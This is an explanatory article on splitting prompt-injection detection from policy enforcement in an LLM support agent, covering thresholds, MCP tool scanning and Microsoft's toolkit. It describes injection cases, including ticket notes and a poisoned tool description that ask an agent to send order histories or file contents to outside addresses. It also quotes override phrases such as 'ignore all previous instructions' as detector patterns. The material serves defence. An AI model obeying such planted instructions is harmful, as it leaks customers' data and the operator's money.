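# Splitting prompt-injection detection from policy enforcement in LLM applications

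## What the two layers are and where they sit

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model (LLM). The attacker writes text that the model will read, and the model follows it as though it came from the developer or the user. If the software only displays the model's answers, the worst result is a bad answer. Many applications now run the model as an agent, in a loop where it can request actions through tools. These tools are functions that look up records, send messages or move money, so an injected sentence can cause somebody to lose money.

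Developers can use two components to defend an LLM application against prompt injection. A guardrail inspects text going into or out of the model and estimates whether it is an attack. A policy engine runs outside the model and allows or denies each action the model requests, using fixed rules about the tool, its arguments and the identity behind the request.

For example, an online retailer might run a support agent that signed-in customers message through a chat window. The agent has four tools. `read_ticket` returns the correspondence filed under a support ticket, `get_order` returns an order's contents, price and date, `issue_refund` pays money back, and `send_email` sends a message from the retailer's address. The retailer lets the agent refund less than $500 within 90 days of the order. All other refunds go to a member of staff. A ticket holds the customer's messages and anything else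 sent to the support address under that ticket's number, such as a note from the courier or a marketplace seller.

### One request from message to reply

*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes the agent's loop in six steps: receive prompts, retrieve documents, reason, generate a tool call, execute it, and return the result. Retrieval and reasoning are optional. Suppose a customer writes that a $64 kettle from order 48213 arrived cracked, says the photos are in ticket 7731, and asks for a refund.

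The application first assembles the model's input, its context. This contains the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the customer's message and perhaps a help-centre article on returns that a search has turned up. The model may write out some reasoning. It then generates a tool call, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments:

`read_ticket(ticket_id=7731)`

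At this point the model has only produced text in an agreed format, and ordinary software has to parse that text and run the function. The software adds the result to the context and the loop repeats, with `get_order`, then `issue_refund(order_id=48213, amount=64.00)`, then `send_email` to send a confirmation. The loop ends when the model writes a reply to the customer without requesting another function.

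| Stage | Where a guardrail can inspect text | Where software can stop an action |
|---|---|---|
| Customer's message | Before the model reads it | No action yet |
| Retrieved help article | Before it enters the context | No action yet |
| Proposed tool call | In free-text arguments, such as an email body | Here, before the function runs |
| Tool result | Before it enters the context | Too late for this call |
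| Reply | Before the customer sees it | No tool call to stop |

An application can inspect text in many places, but it can stop a tool call only at the enforcement point, where the call waits for a decision. A check that runs after `issue_refund` can raise an alarm but can't stop the payment. WithSecure (2024), a security consultancy, describes much the same layout in a one-page guide to defending LLM applications. The guide lists input and output inspection, followed by restricted access, downstream checks and narrow limits on what each function will accept.

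### Injection, direct and indirect, and jailbreaks

In a direct prompt injection, the user types text that tries to override the application's instructions. The customer might claim that a manager has lifted the refund limit and tell the agent to pay out $5,000. In an indirect prompt injection, a third party plants the instructions in content that the agent will read. For example, someone could email the support address and ask whatever assistant processes the ticket to forward the customer's order history to an outside address. The agent would read that request when it calls `read_ticket`. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's LLM to approve it for interview.

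A guardrail that scans only the chat window will miss an injection in the ticket. Researchers have also turned to this indirect route. Of the 37 attack papers that Wang and colleagues collected up to October 2025, 20 deal with it. Wang and colleagues also list a supply-chain route, in which the attacker tampers with the retrieval database or the training data. For the retailer, that could mean an altered help article. Their scheme counts the user's prompt as trusted input, which suits a personal assistant working for its owner but not the retailer, whose users are strangers with an interest in getting refunds.

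A jailbreak is input meant to make a model produce content that it was trained or configured to refuse. Simon Willison, the developer who popularised the term "prompt injection" in 2022, complained in March 2024 that people keep confusing it with jailbreaking (Willison, 2024). *Prompt Injection versus Jailbreaking Definitions* reproduces his definitions, which distinguish the attacks by how they are built. Prompt injection requires an application that joins trusted and untrusted text into one prompt, while a jailbreak targets the model's own safety training. According to Pillar Security's *The terminology problem causing security teams real risks*, however, two widely used catalogues of attacks, OWASP's LLM Top 10 and MITRE ATLAS, classify jailbreaking as prompt injection, and some vendors promise "prompt injection protection" without specifying which attacks they mean.

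Willison's narrower usage is better for splitting detection from enforcement. A customer who coaxes the agent into writing abuse about a competitor has jailbroken it, but no tool has run, so a policy engine has nothing to check.

### Why the model cannot reliably tell instructions from data

Databases had a similar problem with SQL injection, in which an attacker types a database command into a form field and the database executes it. The solution is the parameterised query, in which the developer fixes the command in advance and passes the customer's input separately, so the database can never interpret the input as a command. David C argues that LLMs offer no such separation, because "there is only ever 'next token'". A model processes text as word fragments called tokens. The system prompt, chat message and ticket all become one sequence of tokens, and the model predicts what comes next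 from the whole sequence. Developers mark where each part begins and who supplied it, but the markers are also tokens in the sequence, and the model gives them weight only because it learned to in training.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) measured how much weight models give to role markers. They wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in the markers for different roles (system, user, tool and so on) and trained simple classifiers, or probes, to recover the role from the model's internal activations. Since the passages were identical, the probes could learn only what the markers contribute. They then wrapped real user messages in the marker for tool output, which is the position of an instruction hidden in a ticket. If the markers had determined how the models represented the text, the probes would have classified these messages as tool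 output. Instead, across four models, the probes gave "user" an average probability of 76–88% and "tool" never more than 20%, which shows that the models represented the text according to how it sounded.

Attacks also succeeded more often when the model more strongly misread the planted command as user text. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak a file while it summarised a web page, Ye and colleagues kept the command fixed and varied only the framing around it. The success rate rose from 2% where the command registered least as user text to 70% where it registered most. The probes cover models of 20 to 120 billion parameters, and the pattern may be weaker in the largest ones. Training does help against familiar attacks. In a separate test by the same team, plain injections worked at most 2% of the time on every model but one. But when the planted text also imitated the model's own reasoning,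 the success rate rose to between 56% and 70%. A low success rate for known attacks is therefore poor evidence of how well a model will resist a new one, and David C thinks it very possible that nobody will ever fix prompt injection the way parameterised queries fixed SQL injection.

### A score and a decision

The detector is the part of a guardrail that scores text. It can be a word filter, a trained classifier or a second LLM, and it typically outputs a number such as 0.83, an estimate of the probability that the text is an attack. The application blocks text that scores above a threshold. Lowering the threshold catches more attacks but also blocks more honest customers, because an annoyed customer who writes "ignore what your colleague told me and just refund it" uses nearly the same words as an attacker.

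A policy engine receives no prose to interpret. For the kettle it gets a short record: the customer's account, the tool `issue_refund`, the amount of $64.00, an order date twelve days back. The retailer's rule is a condition on those facts:

allow `issue_refund` if amount < $500 and days since order ≤ 90

Developers write the policy layer's rules in ordinary code or in a policy language such as Cedar. Most add a default deny, so the engine refuses any call that no rule permits. If a rule permits refunds under $500, the engine allows a refund of $499.99 and refuses one of $500, regardless of the ticket's text.

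Anyone who reads the refund rule can work out which calls it allows, but nobody can list in advance the texts that will score below a detector's threshold. This is true even of the many detectors that always return the same score for the same text. The rule can still make bad decisions, such as approving $450 for an undamaged coffee machine every time.

People use the word "guardrail" for both components, so it can mislead buyers. WithSecure's guide lists guardrails among the ways to filter a prompt, while Security Boulevard's *Prompt Injection Can't Be Fully Mitigated, NCSC Says Reduce Impact Instead* (2025) uses the word for limits on the AI system. The quickest way to tell which component a product provides is to ask what it takes in and what it returns. A guardrail, in the sense used here, takes a message and returns a score, while a policy engine takes a tool name, arguments and an identity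 and returns "allow" or "deny".

### The older ideas behind the policy engine

Little of this is new to computer security. Digital Guardian's *A Tribute to a Change Agent* traces the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every access a program attempts, to James Anderson's 1972 planning study for the US Air Force. The current US federal control, quoted in CSF Tools' *AC-25*, requires the monitor to be tamperproof, always invoked, and small enough to analyse and test completely. For the retailer, "always invoked" means that every route to the payment system must pass through the enforcement point, including any route used by an old overnight script. The size requirement rules out an LLM as the monitor, because no one can completely test a model that large.

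*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) uses the word "principal" for the entity to which a system grants authorisations, and which is therefore accountable for what happens under them. In the example, the principal is the signed-in customer. Two of the paper's design principles, as quoted in *Saltzer and Schroeder Principles*, are also relevant. Complete mediation requires a check on every access to every object. Least privilege requires every program to run with the smallest set of privileges its job needs, so a support agent gets no tool for deleting accounts, however well it behaves.

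The term "confused deputy" comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which tells a nearly true story about a compiler at a timesharing company. The compiler had permission to write in its home directory because it kept usage statistics there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the billing records were lost. All of the code worked as intended. Hardy's diagnosis was that the compiler held authority from two sources, the company and the user, and could not indicate which one it was using for a given write.

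The support agent is in the same position because it has the retailer's authority to pay refunds and takes refund requests from strangers. Hardy could repair his compiler by making it present a specific permission with each file it opened. David C calls the LLM an "inherently confusable deputy" because no equivalent repair exists inside the model, and he concludes that designers should put more effort into deterministic limits on actions than into keeping malicious text out. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) go further in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, arguing that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, it should be impossible for that input to trigger any consequential action. Taken literally, this would stop the retailer's agent from basing refund decisions on what a ticket says, which is most of its work. The split gives a weaker guarantee,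 that a ticket may influence which permitted refund the agent proposes but cannot enlarge the set of permitted refunds.

### Layers that fail for different reasons

Defence in depth means stacking controls so that one catches what another lets through. It works well only if they fail for different reasons. Suppose that each of two detectors misses 10% of attacks. If their misses were independent, 1% of attacks would get past both. The general formula is

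P(both miss) = P(first misses) × P(second misses, given that the first missed)

and the last factor is the one to worry about. An attacker who rewords a message until the first detector passes it has probably gone some way towards fooling a second one that learned from similar examples. In the worst case the second detector adds nothing and the figure stays at 10%. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues grant that a detector raises the bar, since the attacker has to deceive it as well as the agent's model, but they see no guarantee in it.

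Rewording an injected prompt doesn't change what the refund rule allows. A policy engine fails when the rule is too generous, when a tool bypasses the enforcement point, or when the rules permit a harmful call. A guardrail can catch some of these cases, such as a planted note that steers the agent towards a $300 refund nobody asked for. Wang and colleagues tested eight defences and found a similar division of weaknesses. Text filters added little overhead but failed against more sophisticated attacks, while execution controls enforced strict limits and often slowed the agent or made it refuse complex tasks.

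To remain independent, the engine has to get the order date from the retailer's order database. If it takes the date from an argument that the model fills in, an injected ticket that misleads the model can also make a two-year-old order appear twelve days old.

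## Deciding which layer answers for which attack

To assign an attack to a layer, a designer can start with the facts needed for a correct decision. Recognising a request for abusive text requires interpreting its wording, so the guardrail handles it. The retailer can refuse a $5,000 refund knowing only the tool, the amount, the order and the principal (here the signed-in customer), regardless of what the customer says, so the policy engine handles that request.

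Some decisions need a fact that neither component has. Checking whether the kettle arrived cracked requires the photos and perhaps the courier's records, and a member of staff may have to look at them. Recording such a case as a gap is better than assigning it to a layer that lacks the information to decide it.

The designer then has to consider what a wrong decision costs. Blocking an honest customer's message costs some goodwill and perhaps a phone call. Sending someone's order history to a stranger can't be undone. Where the loss is money, a rough formula helps:

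expected loss = attempts × share that succeed × loss per success

A detector reduces the share of attacks that succeed, and a refund rule caps the loss from each success. Suppose customers make 200 attempts a month to talk the agent into a $5,000 refund, and the agent grants every request that isn't blocked. With only a detector that misses 5% of the attempts, ten succeed and the retailer loses $50,000. With only a rule that keeps each refund under $500, all 200 customers can still get $499.99, and the retailer loses almost $100,000. With both, the loss is about $5,000.

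But the 5% comes from attacks the retailer has already seen. If customers find a wording that the detector always misses, the detector alone allows a loss of $1 million, while the rule still keeps the loss below $100,000. So the policy engine should be the primary layer, and the guardrail the second, wherever a fixed rule can express the limit.

The system prompt is not a layer in this sense, even if it tells the model never to refund more than $500. In April 2026 Microsoft published an internal test in which safety instructions in the prompt were the only defence. The test used 45 adversarial prompts and 15 valid ones, and 12 of the adversarial prompts (26.67%) led to a policy violation. The test was small and Microsoft has an alternative to promote, but the result fits the earlier point that a model gives instructions weight only because it learned to.

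### Ten attacks on the support agent

| Attack or failure | Primary layer | Second layer | What remains |
|---|---|---|---|
| Jailbreak for harmful text | Guardrail on message and reply | The model's own safety training | Wording that scores below the threshold |
| Direct injection in the chat | Policy engine, on amount and order date | Guardrail on the chat | An undeserved refund under $500 |
| Indirect injection in a ticket | Policy engine, on recipient and amount | Guardrail on tool results | A planted note that steers a permitted refund |
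| Hidden instructions in a tool description | Guardrail, before the model reads the description | Policy engine, on the calls that follow | Plainly worded instructions that lead to permitted calls |
| Forbidden tool | Policy engine, by default deny | No credentials for that tool | Routes that skip the enforcement point |
| Permitted tool, bad arguments | Policy engine, on each argument | Guardrail on free text such as an email body | Wrong values inside the allowed range |
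| Use of another customer's rights | Policy engine, on the signed-in account | The order database's own access check | A stolen account |
| Leak through several permitted calls | Policy engine, if it has the session's history | Guardrail on outgoing text | Gradual or paraphrased leaks |
| False statement in a permitted email | Guardrail that compares the text with order records | Staff review | Claims that no record can settle |
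| The model's own error, with no attacker | Policy engine, on the ordinary rules | Staff spot checks | Mistakes within the rules |

Injection goes to the policy engine first, even though detectors exist to catch it. The retailer mostly needs to decide whether money or data should leave, and it can do that without knowing whether a message was an attack. But if the injected text is meant to change only the reply, for instance by getting the agent to give customers a fraudster's phone number, the guardrail has to catch it because there is no tool call for the policy engine to check.

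A detector is close to useless against someone using another customer's rights. "Can you tell me where order 48214 has got to?" is a polite question, and it is an attack only if the order belongs to somebody else. The policy engine can check this by comparing the order's owner with the signed-in account.

Permission checks do little against false statements. If an agent falsely tells a customer by email that the warranty covers accidental damage for ten years, the email passes those checks because the tool is permitted, the recipient is correct and the principal is authorized. An attack detector won't help either, because the sentence reads like ordinary customer service. A check against the warranty terms might catch the error, but somebody has to build such a check for each kind of claim.

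When the model makes its own mistake, the guardrail has no hostile text to score. If the model enters a $64 refund as $640, the refund rule blocks it, but the rule would allow a mistaken entry of $94. Because the rule applies to every call, the retailer gets this protection without deciding whether an attacker was involved.

### How Microsoft divides the work

Microsoft publishes a similar division for its Agent Governance Toolkit, which it released in April under an open-source licence (Microsoft, 2026). The toolkit checks an agent's tool calls against policy before they run, so it blocks a call to `delete_file` if a policy forbids it. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries* describes the toolkit as governing what agents do, not what they "think or say".

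According to the same document, the toolkit does not detect invented content passed to a permitted tool (such as the ten-year warranty), indirect prompt injection that corrupts the agent's reasoning, or a harmful sequence of individually permitted actions. For the last case, Microsoft gives the example of an agent that is allowed to read a database and post to Slack, and can therefore post the customer list in a public channel.

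The toolkit also does not track which documents influenced a decision or whether they were confidential. For example, a staff member might add an internal note to ticket 7731 saying that the customer may be a fraudster. The agent is allowed to read the ticket and email the customer, so the toolkit's ordinary rules do not stop it from quoting the note to them.

To fill some of these gaps, Microsoft tells users to add a model-safety layer, such as Azure AI Content Safety or Llama Guard, to filter input and output. It recommends putting the toolkit next, then the application's own code, which validates business logic, and then containers and network rules. The application's code would handle the decision about the cracked kettle.

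The arrangement doesn't make clear which layer should block prompt injection. Microsoft says the safety layer catches hallucinations and toxic content, but doesn't mention injection there. It separately recommends a tool that tests an agent for injection weaknesses, but testing doesn't block attacks. A retailer that follows the advice has to check that the filter it buys screens for indirect injection and that its developers have connected the filter to the results of `read_ticket`.

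### Which of these limits still hold

The limitations document dates from May 2026 at the latest. Rubinlake's *Agent Governance Toolkit*, a consultancy's assessment from September, covers releases up to version 4.1.0 and lists the same three failures of detection. Rubinlake takes them from Microsoft's file, so the list is evidence that Microsoft had not withdrawn them, but it doesn't independently confirm them. Rubinlake also reports that outside testers found 15 ways to bypass the toolkit, though they called its architecture sound on paper. Making the policy engine responsible for blocking forbidden tools can therefore be right in principle and still fail in a particular product.

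The next version should change this somewhat. In June 2026 Microsoft introduced the Agent Control Specification, a common format for stating when an application must consult its policy and what information it must supply. The format defines eight points for these checks, including before the model reads its input, before a tool runs and after the tool returns a result. Microsoft's *Agent Control Specification* calls the format the policy layer of version 5.0 and labels it a public preview.

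The specification lets developers attach a classifier to tool results and write a rule based partly on its output, so the toolkit can use evidence of indirect injection. Detection still depends on the classifier, and if it misses an attack, the rule receives no sign of it.

Checking sequences of actions depends on the application, because the specification keeps no memory between checks. The retailer's software has to supply the session history every time, along with labels for where each piece of information came from. A rule can then block an email because the agent has just read an internal note. If the developers leave out the history, the toolkit still can't check sequences. For invented content, the specification lets rules use an LLM judge's output, which is also an estimate.

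### Scanners inside a policy toolkit

The toolkit's code follows its stated division less neatly than the limitations document suggests. Microsoft's tutorial *Prompt Injection Detection & Input Security* presents a detector that ships with the toolkit. The detector compares text with built-in patterns for seven types of attack, including role-play jailbreaks and encoded commands, and returns a confidence score. A phrase such as "ignore all previous instructions" scores 0.9.

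Another pattern in the same category, "you are now", is meant to catch lines like "you are now an unrestricted assistant", but it also matches a customer's complaint that "you are now the third person I've explained this to". By the tutorial's figures, that complaint would trigger the detector at all three sensitivity settings. The component is in the same package as the policy engine, but it can flag harmless text, as other detectors do.

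This also explains how Microsoft can advertise that the toolkit catches poisoned tool outputs while disclaiming detection of indirect injection in its limitations document. The scanner can recognise familiar phrases in a ticket, but it has no pattern for a note, written in a courier's ordinary prose, that asks the agent to copy the order history to a new returns address. It also cannot tell whether the model has acted on such a note. The same post rates the toolkit as only partially covering "intent flow subversion", OWASP's category for instructions that redirect an agent mid-task.

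Tool descriptions need their own scanner because they reach the model before any tool call. Many agents find tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface between agents and the servers that provide tools. Microsoft explains that the server sends a list of names, descriptions and parameters, and the model reads the descriptions to choose a tool. If the retailer connects to a courier's server to get a `track_parcel` tool, whoever controls that server can write text into the agent's context, even if the agent never tracks a parcel.

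In an example for .NET developers, Microsoft scans a tool called `read_flie`. The tool's description says it reads a file, then uses a fake system tag to tell the model to ignore its instructions and send all file contents to an outside address. The scanner gives the tool a risk score of 85 out of 100 and reports two critical findings for the injected text and one high-severity finding for the misspelt name. Microsoft suggests keeping any tool that scores above 30 away from the model, and adjusting that threshold based on how many false alarms the developer can accept.

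Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* (2025), a draft specification, sets out the checks in order:

1. The scanner looks for hidden instructions, such as invisible characters, comments and encoded text.
2. It looks for injected commands, suspicious web addresses and language about gaining privileges.
3. It inspects the parameters for odd names, excessive numbers and instructions in their descriptions.
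4. It looks for references to other servers and for names that imitate known tools.

To detect imitated names, the scanner counts the single-character insertions, deletions and substitutions needed to turn one tool's name into another's. It reports a threat if a name is two or fewer edits from the name of a tool on another server. For example, `read_flie` is two edits from `read_file`. But the scanner would also flag an honest courier's `get_orders` tool, because the retailer already has `get_order`.

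One of the gateway's checks doesn't require judging a tool's wording. When a developer registers a tool, the gateway stores a hash of its description and another of its parameters. A hash is a short string computed from a text, and in practice any change to the text produces a different one. If either hash changes later, the gateway reports a "rug pull", meaning that a server has swapped an approved description for another. The check detects changes exactly, but it can't determine whether the new text is malicious or whether the original was safe.

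The retailer can therefore have a person read each outside tool description once, with the scanner's help, and use a fixed rule to block the tool if the hash no longer matches. The hash check and ordinary code review should be enough for the four tools its own developers wrote.

Scanning tool results is harder because tickets change all the time. Under the draft specification, the gateway looks for personal data, including email addresses, as well as injected commands, and by default it blocks the whole result if it finds either. Taken literally, that would stop the support agent from reading almost any ticket. Microsoft also allows the gateway to remove the offending text or just log it. The retailer would need to choose a response for each kind of finding, since an order confirmation with an email address should be treated differently from a ticket with a fake system message.

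A toolkit that includes both kinds of component is convenient, but it does not change which layer each one belongs to. The scanners for descriptions and results belong with the guardrail and have a threshold and an error rate to measure. The hash check and the list of permitted tools belong with the policy engine.

### Causes and effects

The table of ten attacks mixes causes with effects. "Indirect injection" is a cause, text planted by a third party, while "permitted tool, bad arguments" is an effect. A policy engine receives only effects. When the agent proposes `send_email` to an outside address, the engine gets the same record whether the proposal resulted from a planted note, a lying customer or the model's own mistake. One incident can therefore belong in two rows, and the question of which layer handles indirect injection has no single answer.

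After reviewing 116 papers, Chu (2026) similarly argues in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* that lists of attack types do not show a designer where to put the controls. "Adversarial input", for instance, covers both a mathematically altered input to the model and a poisoned document in the agent's memory. The defence against the altered input belongs in the model, while the defence against the poisoned document belongs in the software that manages memory. Chu instead proposes dividing the agent's architecture into seven layers, and claims to prove that a control at one layer cannot detect an attack confined to another.

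The claim is about detection, but a control can often stop an attack without detecting it. The refund rule cannot detect a planted note, yet it blocks the $5,000 refund requested in the note. This sort of injection also crosses layers, entering as text and leaving as an action, so the retailer has a chance to stop it at both points.

Assigning each attack twice, by cause and by effect, answers the objection. For causes, the retailer lists the places where outside text enters: the chat, tickets, help articles, tool descriptions and the results of other tools. For effects, it lists what it wants to prevent, such as an excessive refund, a payment to the wrong account, an email to an outsider, access to a stranger's order and a false promise to a customer. Any of the five entry points could lead to any of the five effects, which makes 25 combinations. Ten controls, one for each entry point and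 one for each effect, can cover them all, though imperfectly, because a scan can check incoming text without identifying the action it is meant to cause, and a rule can restrict an action whatever text caused it.

Microsoft's more recent plans are consistent with this. Help Net Security's *Microsoft wants to limit AI agents' permissions when they stray from the job* (2026) describes permissions that shrink or expire with the task. It adds that an agent with appropriate access can still encounter a malicious instruction in an outside document, so controls have to examine both the information exchanged and where it goes.

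Published attack statistics mix causes and effects too. Mondaq's *Every AI Agent In Your Enterprise Needs A Human* reports figures that Microsoft collected from AI workloads on its Azure cloud over 90 days. Malicious links inserted through model and tool outputs made up 52% of the attack activity, jailbreaks 16%, abuse of tools and agents 12%, and abuse of identities and credentials 10%. These figures cover only what Microsoft noticed on its own cloud, and they don't show which attacks succeeded or how much damage they did.

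Still, the links are a useful case for assigning an attack to both layers. To address the cause, the retailer scans tool results for text that tries to insert a link. To limit the effect, it can allow replies and emails to link only to its own website and the courier's. Ordinary code can check a link's domain, even though the surrounding sentence may be impossible to judge.

Working through both assignments also shows which attacks have only one real control. A jailbreak for harmful text involves no tool call for the policy layer to check, and the model's own error involves no hostile text for the detector to find. If a planted note asks for a believable $300 refund, the rules permit the refund, so only the scan of the ticket can stop the attack. Where such an attack would be expensive, the retailer can limit what the agent can reach. In Help Net Security's *LLM agent security needs more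 than guardrails*, Madhu Shashanka of the security company Concentric AI points out that an agent can't leak a file it can't read. Similarly, if `get_order` never returns payment details, the detector doesn't have to catch attempts to extract them.

The other common answer is to have a person approve the action. According to Mondaq, Microsoft considers overreliance on human review "a systemic risk", partly because the system under attack often controls when review is requested. The retailer should therefore use the $500 rule to send refunds to staff, whether or not the model flags them for review.

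## Setting up injection and jailbreak detection

The detector has to catch the attacks that the policy engine's rules let through. Its success depends on what it reads, how it scores the text, where the retailer sets the threshold and what the application does when it flags something.

### Which texts to scan

Tool results matter most because outsiders can write in them and the agent reads them mid-task. Wang and colleagues rate tool results as untrusted and retrieved documents as partially trusted. The retailer should treat the chat as untrusted too. The retailer's help articles rarely change, so it can scan each one when an employee saves it instead of each time a search returns it.

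Like `read_ticket`, `get_order` can return injected instructions. Its data comes from the retailer's own database, but marketplace sellers write the product names. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (Liu, 2026) tested detectors against this route by adding instructions to product names in a simulated shop. The retailer therefore has to ask who could have written each field, whichever system returns it.

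The detector should also read exactly what the model will read. Of the 37 attack papers that Wang and colleagues reviewed, 27 try to hide the planted text, for instance by encoding it or burying it in a long document. A staff member who opens an email sees the formatted page, but the agent may receive the source code, including white text that the staff member can't see against a white background. If the agent's model accepts images, a text detector will miss an instruction written in a photo.

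The final reply needs a different check. By then an injection has either worked or failed, so this check looks for anything the customer shouldn't see. Content moderation models can do part of this. *BELLS-O* (Waibl, Michalak and Mariaccia, 2026), an independent test of 33 guardrail systems, found that Qwen3Guard-Gen-8B flagged 95.8% of harmful replies and none of the harmless ones. But these models look for categories such as self-harm or hate speech, so they would pass a polite reply that gives out a fraudster's phone number.

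### How a detector arrives at a score

A pattern matcher, like the one in Microsoft's toolkit, usually stores its phrases as regular expressions, which can match variations on a phrase. A developer assigns each pattern a score in advance. The method is fast, but it misses paraphrases. In *Beyond Pattern Matching*, Munirathinam (2026) ran the patterns of prompt-shield, the author's own open-source tool, on 8,276 attack prompts. The patterns caught about 92% of the attacks that openly told the model to override its instructions, but only 35–45% of subtle indirect injections that lacked override keywords.

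Some tools add a vector lookup. They convert the text into a list of numbers representing its meaning and measure how close those numbers are to those of stored attacks. This can catch a reworded attack if a similar one is already stored.

A trained classifier is a fairly small language model that learned from examples labelled as attacks or harmless text. It produces one number for each label, and a standard formula turns the two into a score between 0 and 1:

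score = e^a / (e^a + e^h)

Here a is the number for "attack" and h is the number for "harmless". If a ticket gets a = 2.0 and h = 0.4, the score is 0.83. This score is only loosely a probability, because it depends on how closely the ticket resembles the training examples. PIGuard, an open classifier from 2025, gave a score of 1.00 to a tool result containing only the message "Password updated."

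Classifiers also have a length limit, between 512 and 2,048 tokens for those that Liu tested. Most cut off text past the limit, so an instruction at the bottom of a long ticket never gets a score. Meta's Prompt Guard models split the text into 512-token segments and take the highest score, which covers the whole ticket but gives a long one more chances to cause a false alarm. *PIShield* (2025) reports extremely high false positive rates on long texts for DataSentinel, AttentionTracker and TaskTracker, which use other designs.

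The third option is to ask a language model to act as judge. Liu gave two general-purpose models the user's request and one tool result, and asked whether the result tried to make the assistant do something the user hadn't requested. The score came from the probabilities that the model assigned to its possible first words:

score = P(Yes) / (P(Yes) + P(No))

Because the judge receives the user's request, it can detect that a customer who wants a refund never asked anyone to forward an order history. But it checks only for what its prompt specifies. Liu's prompt was about actions, and one judge caught 61–69% of attacks planted in programming answers but only 1% of injections meant to change how the assistant answered the user. The judge is also a language model processing the attacker's text, so an injection can mislead it. It is also slower than specialised detectors. In tests by Waibl and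 colleagues, nearly all specialised detectors responded within half a second, while all but one of the general-purpose models took longer.

*Enhancing Security in LLM Applications* (2025) compares three tools on attempts to extract a system prompt. LLM Guard, which uses a classifier, caught every attack but raised the most false alarms. Vigil, which uses vector lookup, raised no false alarms but missed more attacks. Rebuff, which uses a language model, fell between the two. The samples cover only this narrow kind of attack, so the ranking may not hold for others, such as instructions planted in tickets.

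### Marking untrusted text for the model

Spotlighting helps the agent's model distinguish outside text from instructions. The application puts delimiters around the text or transforms it in a simple way. For example, it could replace the spaces in ticket 7731 with carets, giving "the^kettle^arrived^cracked", and state in the system prompt that text with carets is information and never an instruction. An attacker who guesses the delimiter can forge a closing one, but can't stop the application from adding carets to every line of the ticket.

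Spotlighting produces no score and blocks nothing. It depends on the model following the marks, and Ye and colleagues' experiments with role markers suggest that it may not always do so. But spotlighting adds little to the input. In a comparison of defences in *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), it raised the average input from 3,764 to 3,914 tokens, or about 4%.

Microsoft announced spotlighting in 2025 as an addition to Prompt Shields, its service for scanning user prompts and third-party documents. Microsoft's *Enhance AI security with Azure Prompt Shields and Azure AI Content Safety* says that spotlighting improves the detection of indirect injection but gives no measured rates. A retailer can reasonably switch it on, but shouldn't loosen the detector's threshold because of it. The retailer should also run its own detector on the text before adding the carets that mark it, because a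 classifier trained on ordinary prose may score the marked version very differently.

### Setting the threshold

The threshold sets both the share of attacks the detector catches and the share of harmless items it flags (the false positive rate). Because attacks are rare, most flagged items can be harmless even when this rate is low.

Suppose that the retailer's agent reads 1,000,000 tool results, of which 100 carry an injection. A detector with a 95% detection rate catches 95 of them. If its false positive rate is 1%, it also flags 9,999 of the 999,900 harmless results. The share of alarms that are real is

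95 / (95 + 9,999) = 0.94%

so staff who investigate the alarms will find an attack in fewer than one case out of a hundred. At a false positive rate of 0.1%, there are about 1,000 false alarms and 8.7% of all alarms are real. For half of them to be real, the detector could flag only 95 harmless results in the whole million.

This arithmetic assumes the detection rate stays at 95%, but raising the threshold usually lowers it, sometimes steeply. On tool results from AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel and banking tasks, PIGuard caught almost three-quarters of the injections and flagged 20% of the harmless results at its default threshold of 0.5. When Liu raised the threshold until PIGuard flagged only 1% of the harmless results, it caught 2.1% of the injections.

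To choose a threshold, the retailer can score 10,000 harmless tool results from its own traffic and set the threshold so that only ten exceed it, a rate of 0.1%. Somebody should read the highest-scoring results first, because a real injection among them would push the threshold too high. Small samples can mislead, because a detector that flags none of n harmless items could still have a false positive rate as high as 3/n, by a common rule of thumb. For the 339 clean AgentDojo results that Liu used, that is nearly 0.9%.

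False alarms also accumulate over a conversation, and one flagged result may be enough to stop the agent. ProtectAI v2, a 2024 classifier, flagged 30% of the harmless AgentDojo results, but 69% of the tasks had at least one of these false alarms.

### Why jailbreaks need their own threshold

The same product can have very different false positive rates on prompt injection and jailbreak datasets. Waibl and colleagues found that Lakera Guard, a commercial detector, caught about 95% of both attacks, but its false positive rate was 14.4% on the injection datasets and 81.9% on the jailbreak datasets.

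The jailbreak figure partly reflects how the researchers labelled the data. They took harmless requests, wrapped them in the role-play and odd encodings that jailbreakers use, and counted any alarm as a false positive. The dedicated detectors reacted to the wrapping, and all of them had a mean false positive rate above 25%. Few of the retailer's customers will write that way, so it should see a lower rate.

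Customers also use words that appear in attacks, and one angry sentence could easily contain three of them. *Safety Reconstructed* (2026) reports results on NotInject, a set of harmless prompts containing such trigger words. The Granite guardrail model flagged 1.77% of the prompts with one trigger word and 10.62% of those with three.

The consequences of a miss also differ. The check on the final reply can still catch abusive text if a jailbreak gets past the scan of the chat, but if a planted note gets past the scan of a ticket and leads to a permitted refund, the retailer has lost the money. The retailer can therefore accept more misses in the jailbreak check than in the injection check, and set each threshold using the texts that the check will read.

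This requires separate scores for injection and jailbreaks. Meta's first Prompt Guard returned a probability for each. If a product returns only a single score, the retailer can at least set one threshold for the chat and another for tool results.

### Blocking, stripping or flagging

Blocking a tool result prevents the agent from reading it. If the result is ticket 7731, the agent can't see the photos or process the refund, so a false alarm leaves the customer's task unfinished unless a member of staff takes over. At a false positive rate of 0.1%, staff would have to handle about 1,000 results per million, which may be affordable, but at 1% they would have to handle about 10,000.

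Stripping removes the suspicious text and passes on the rest. *Indirect Prompt Injections* describes a sanitizer that cleans tool results before the agent reads them. In the developers' own test on AgentDojo, it caught 99.53% of attacks with no false alarms. But AgentDojo's attacks are plainly worded commands addressed to the model, which are easier to recognise than a courier's note in ordinary prose. The average output also rose from 303 tokens without a defence to 1,675. For the retailer, another risk is that the sanitizer deletes the sentence in which the customer describes the damage, and the agent may then refuse a valid refund without anyone knowing why.

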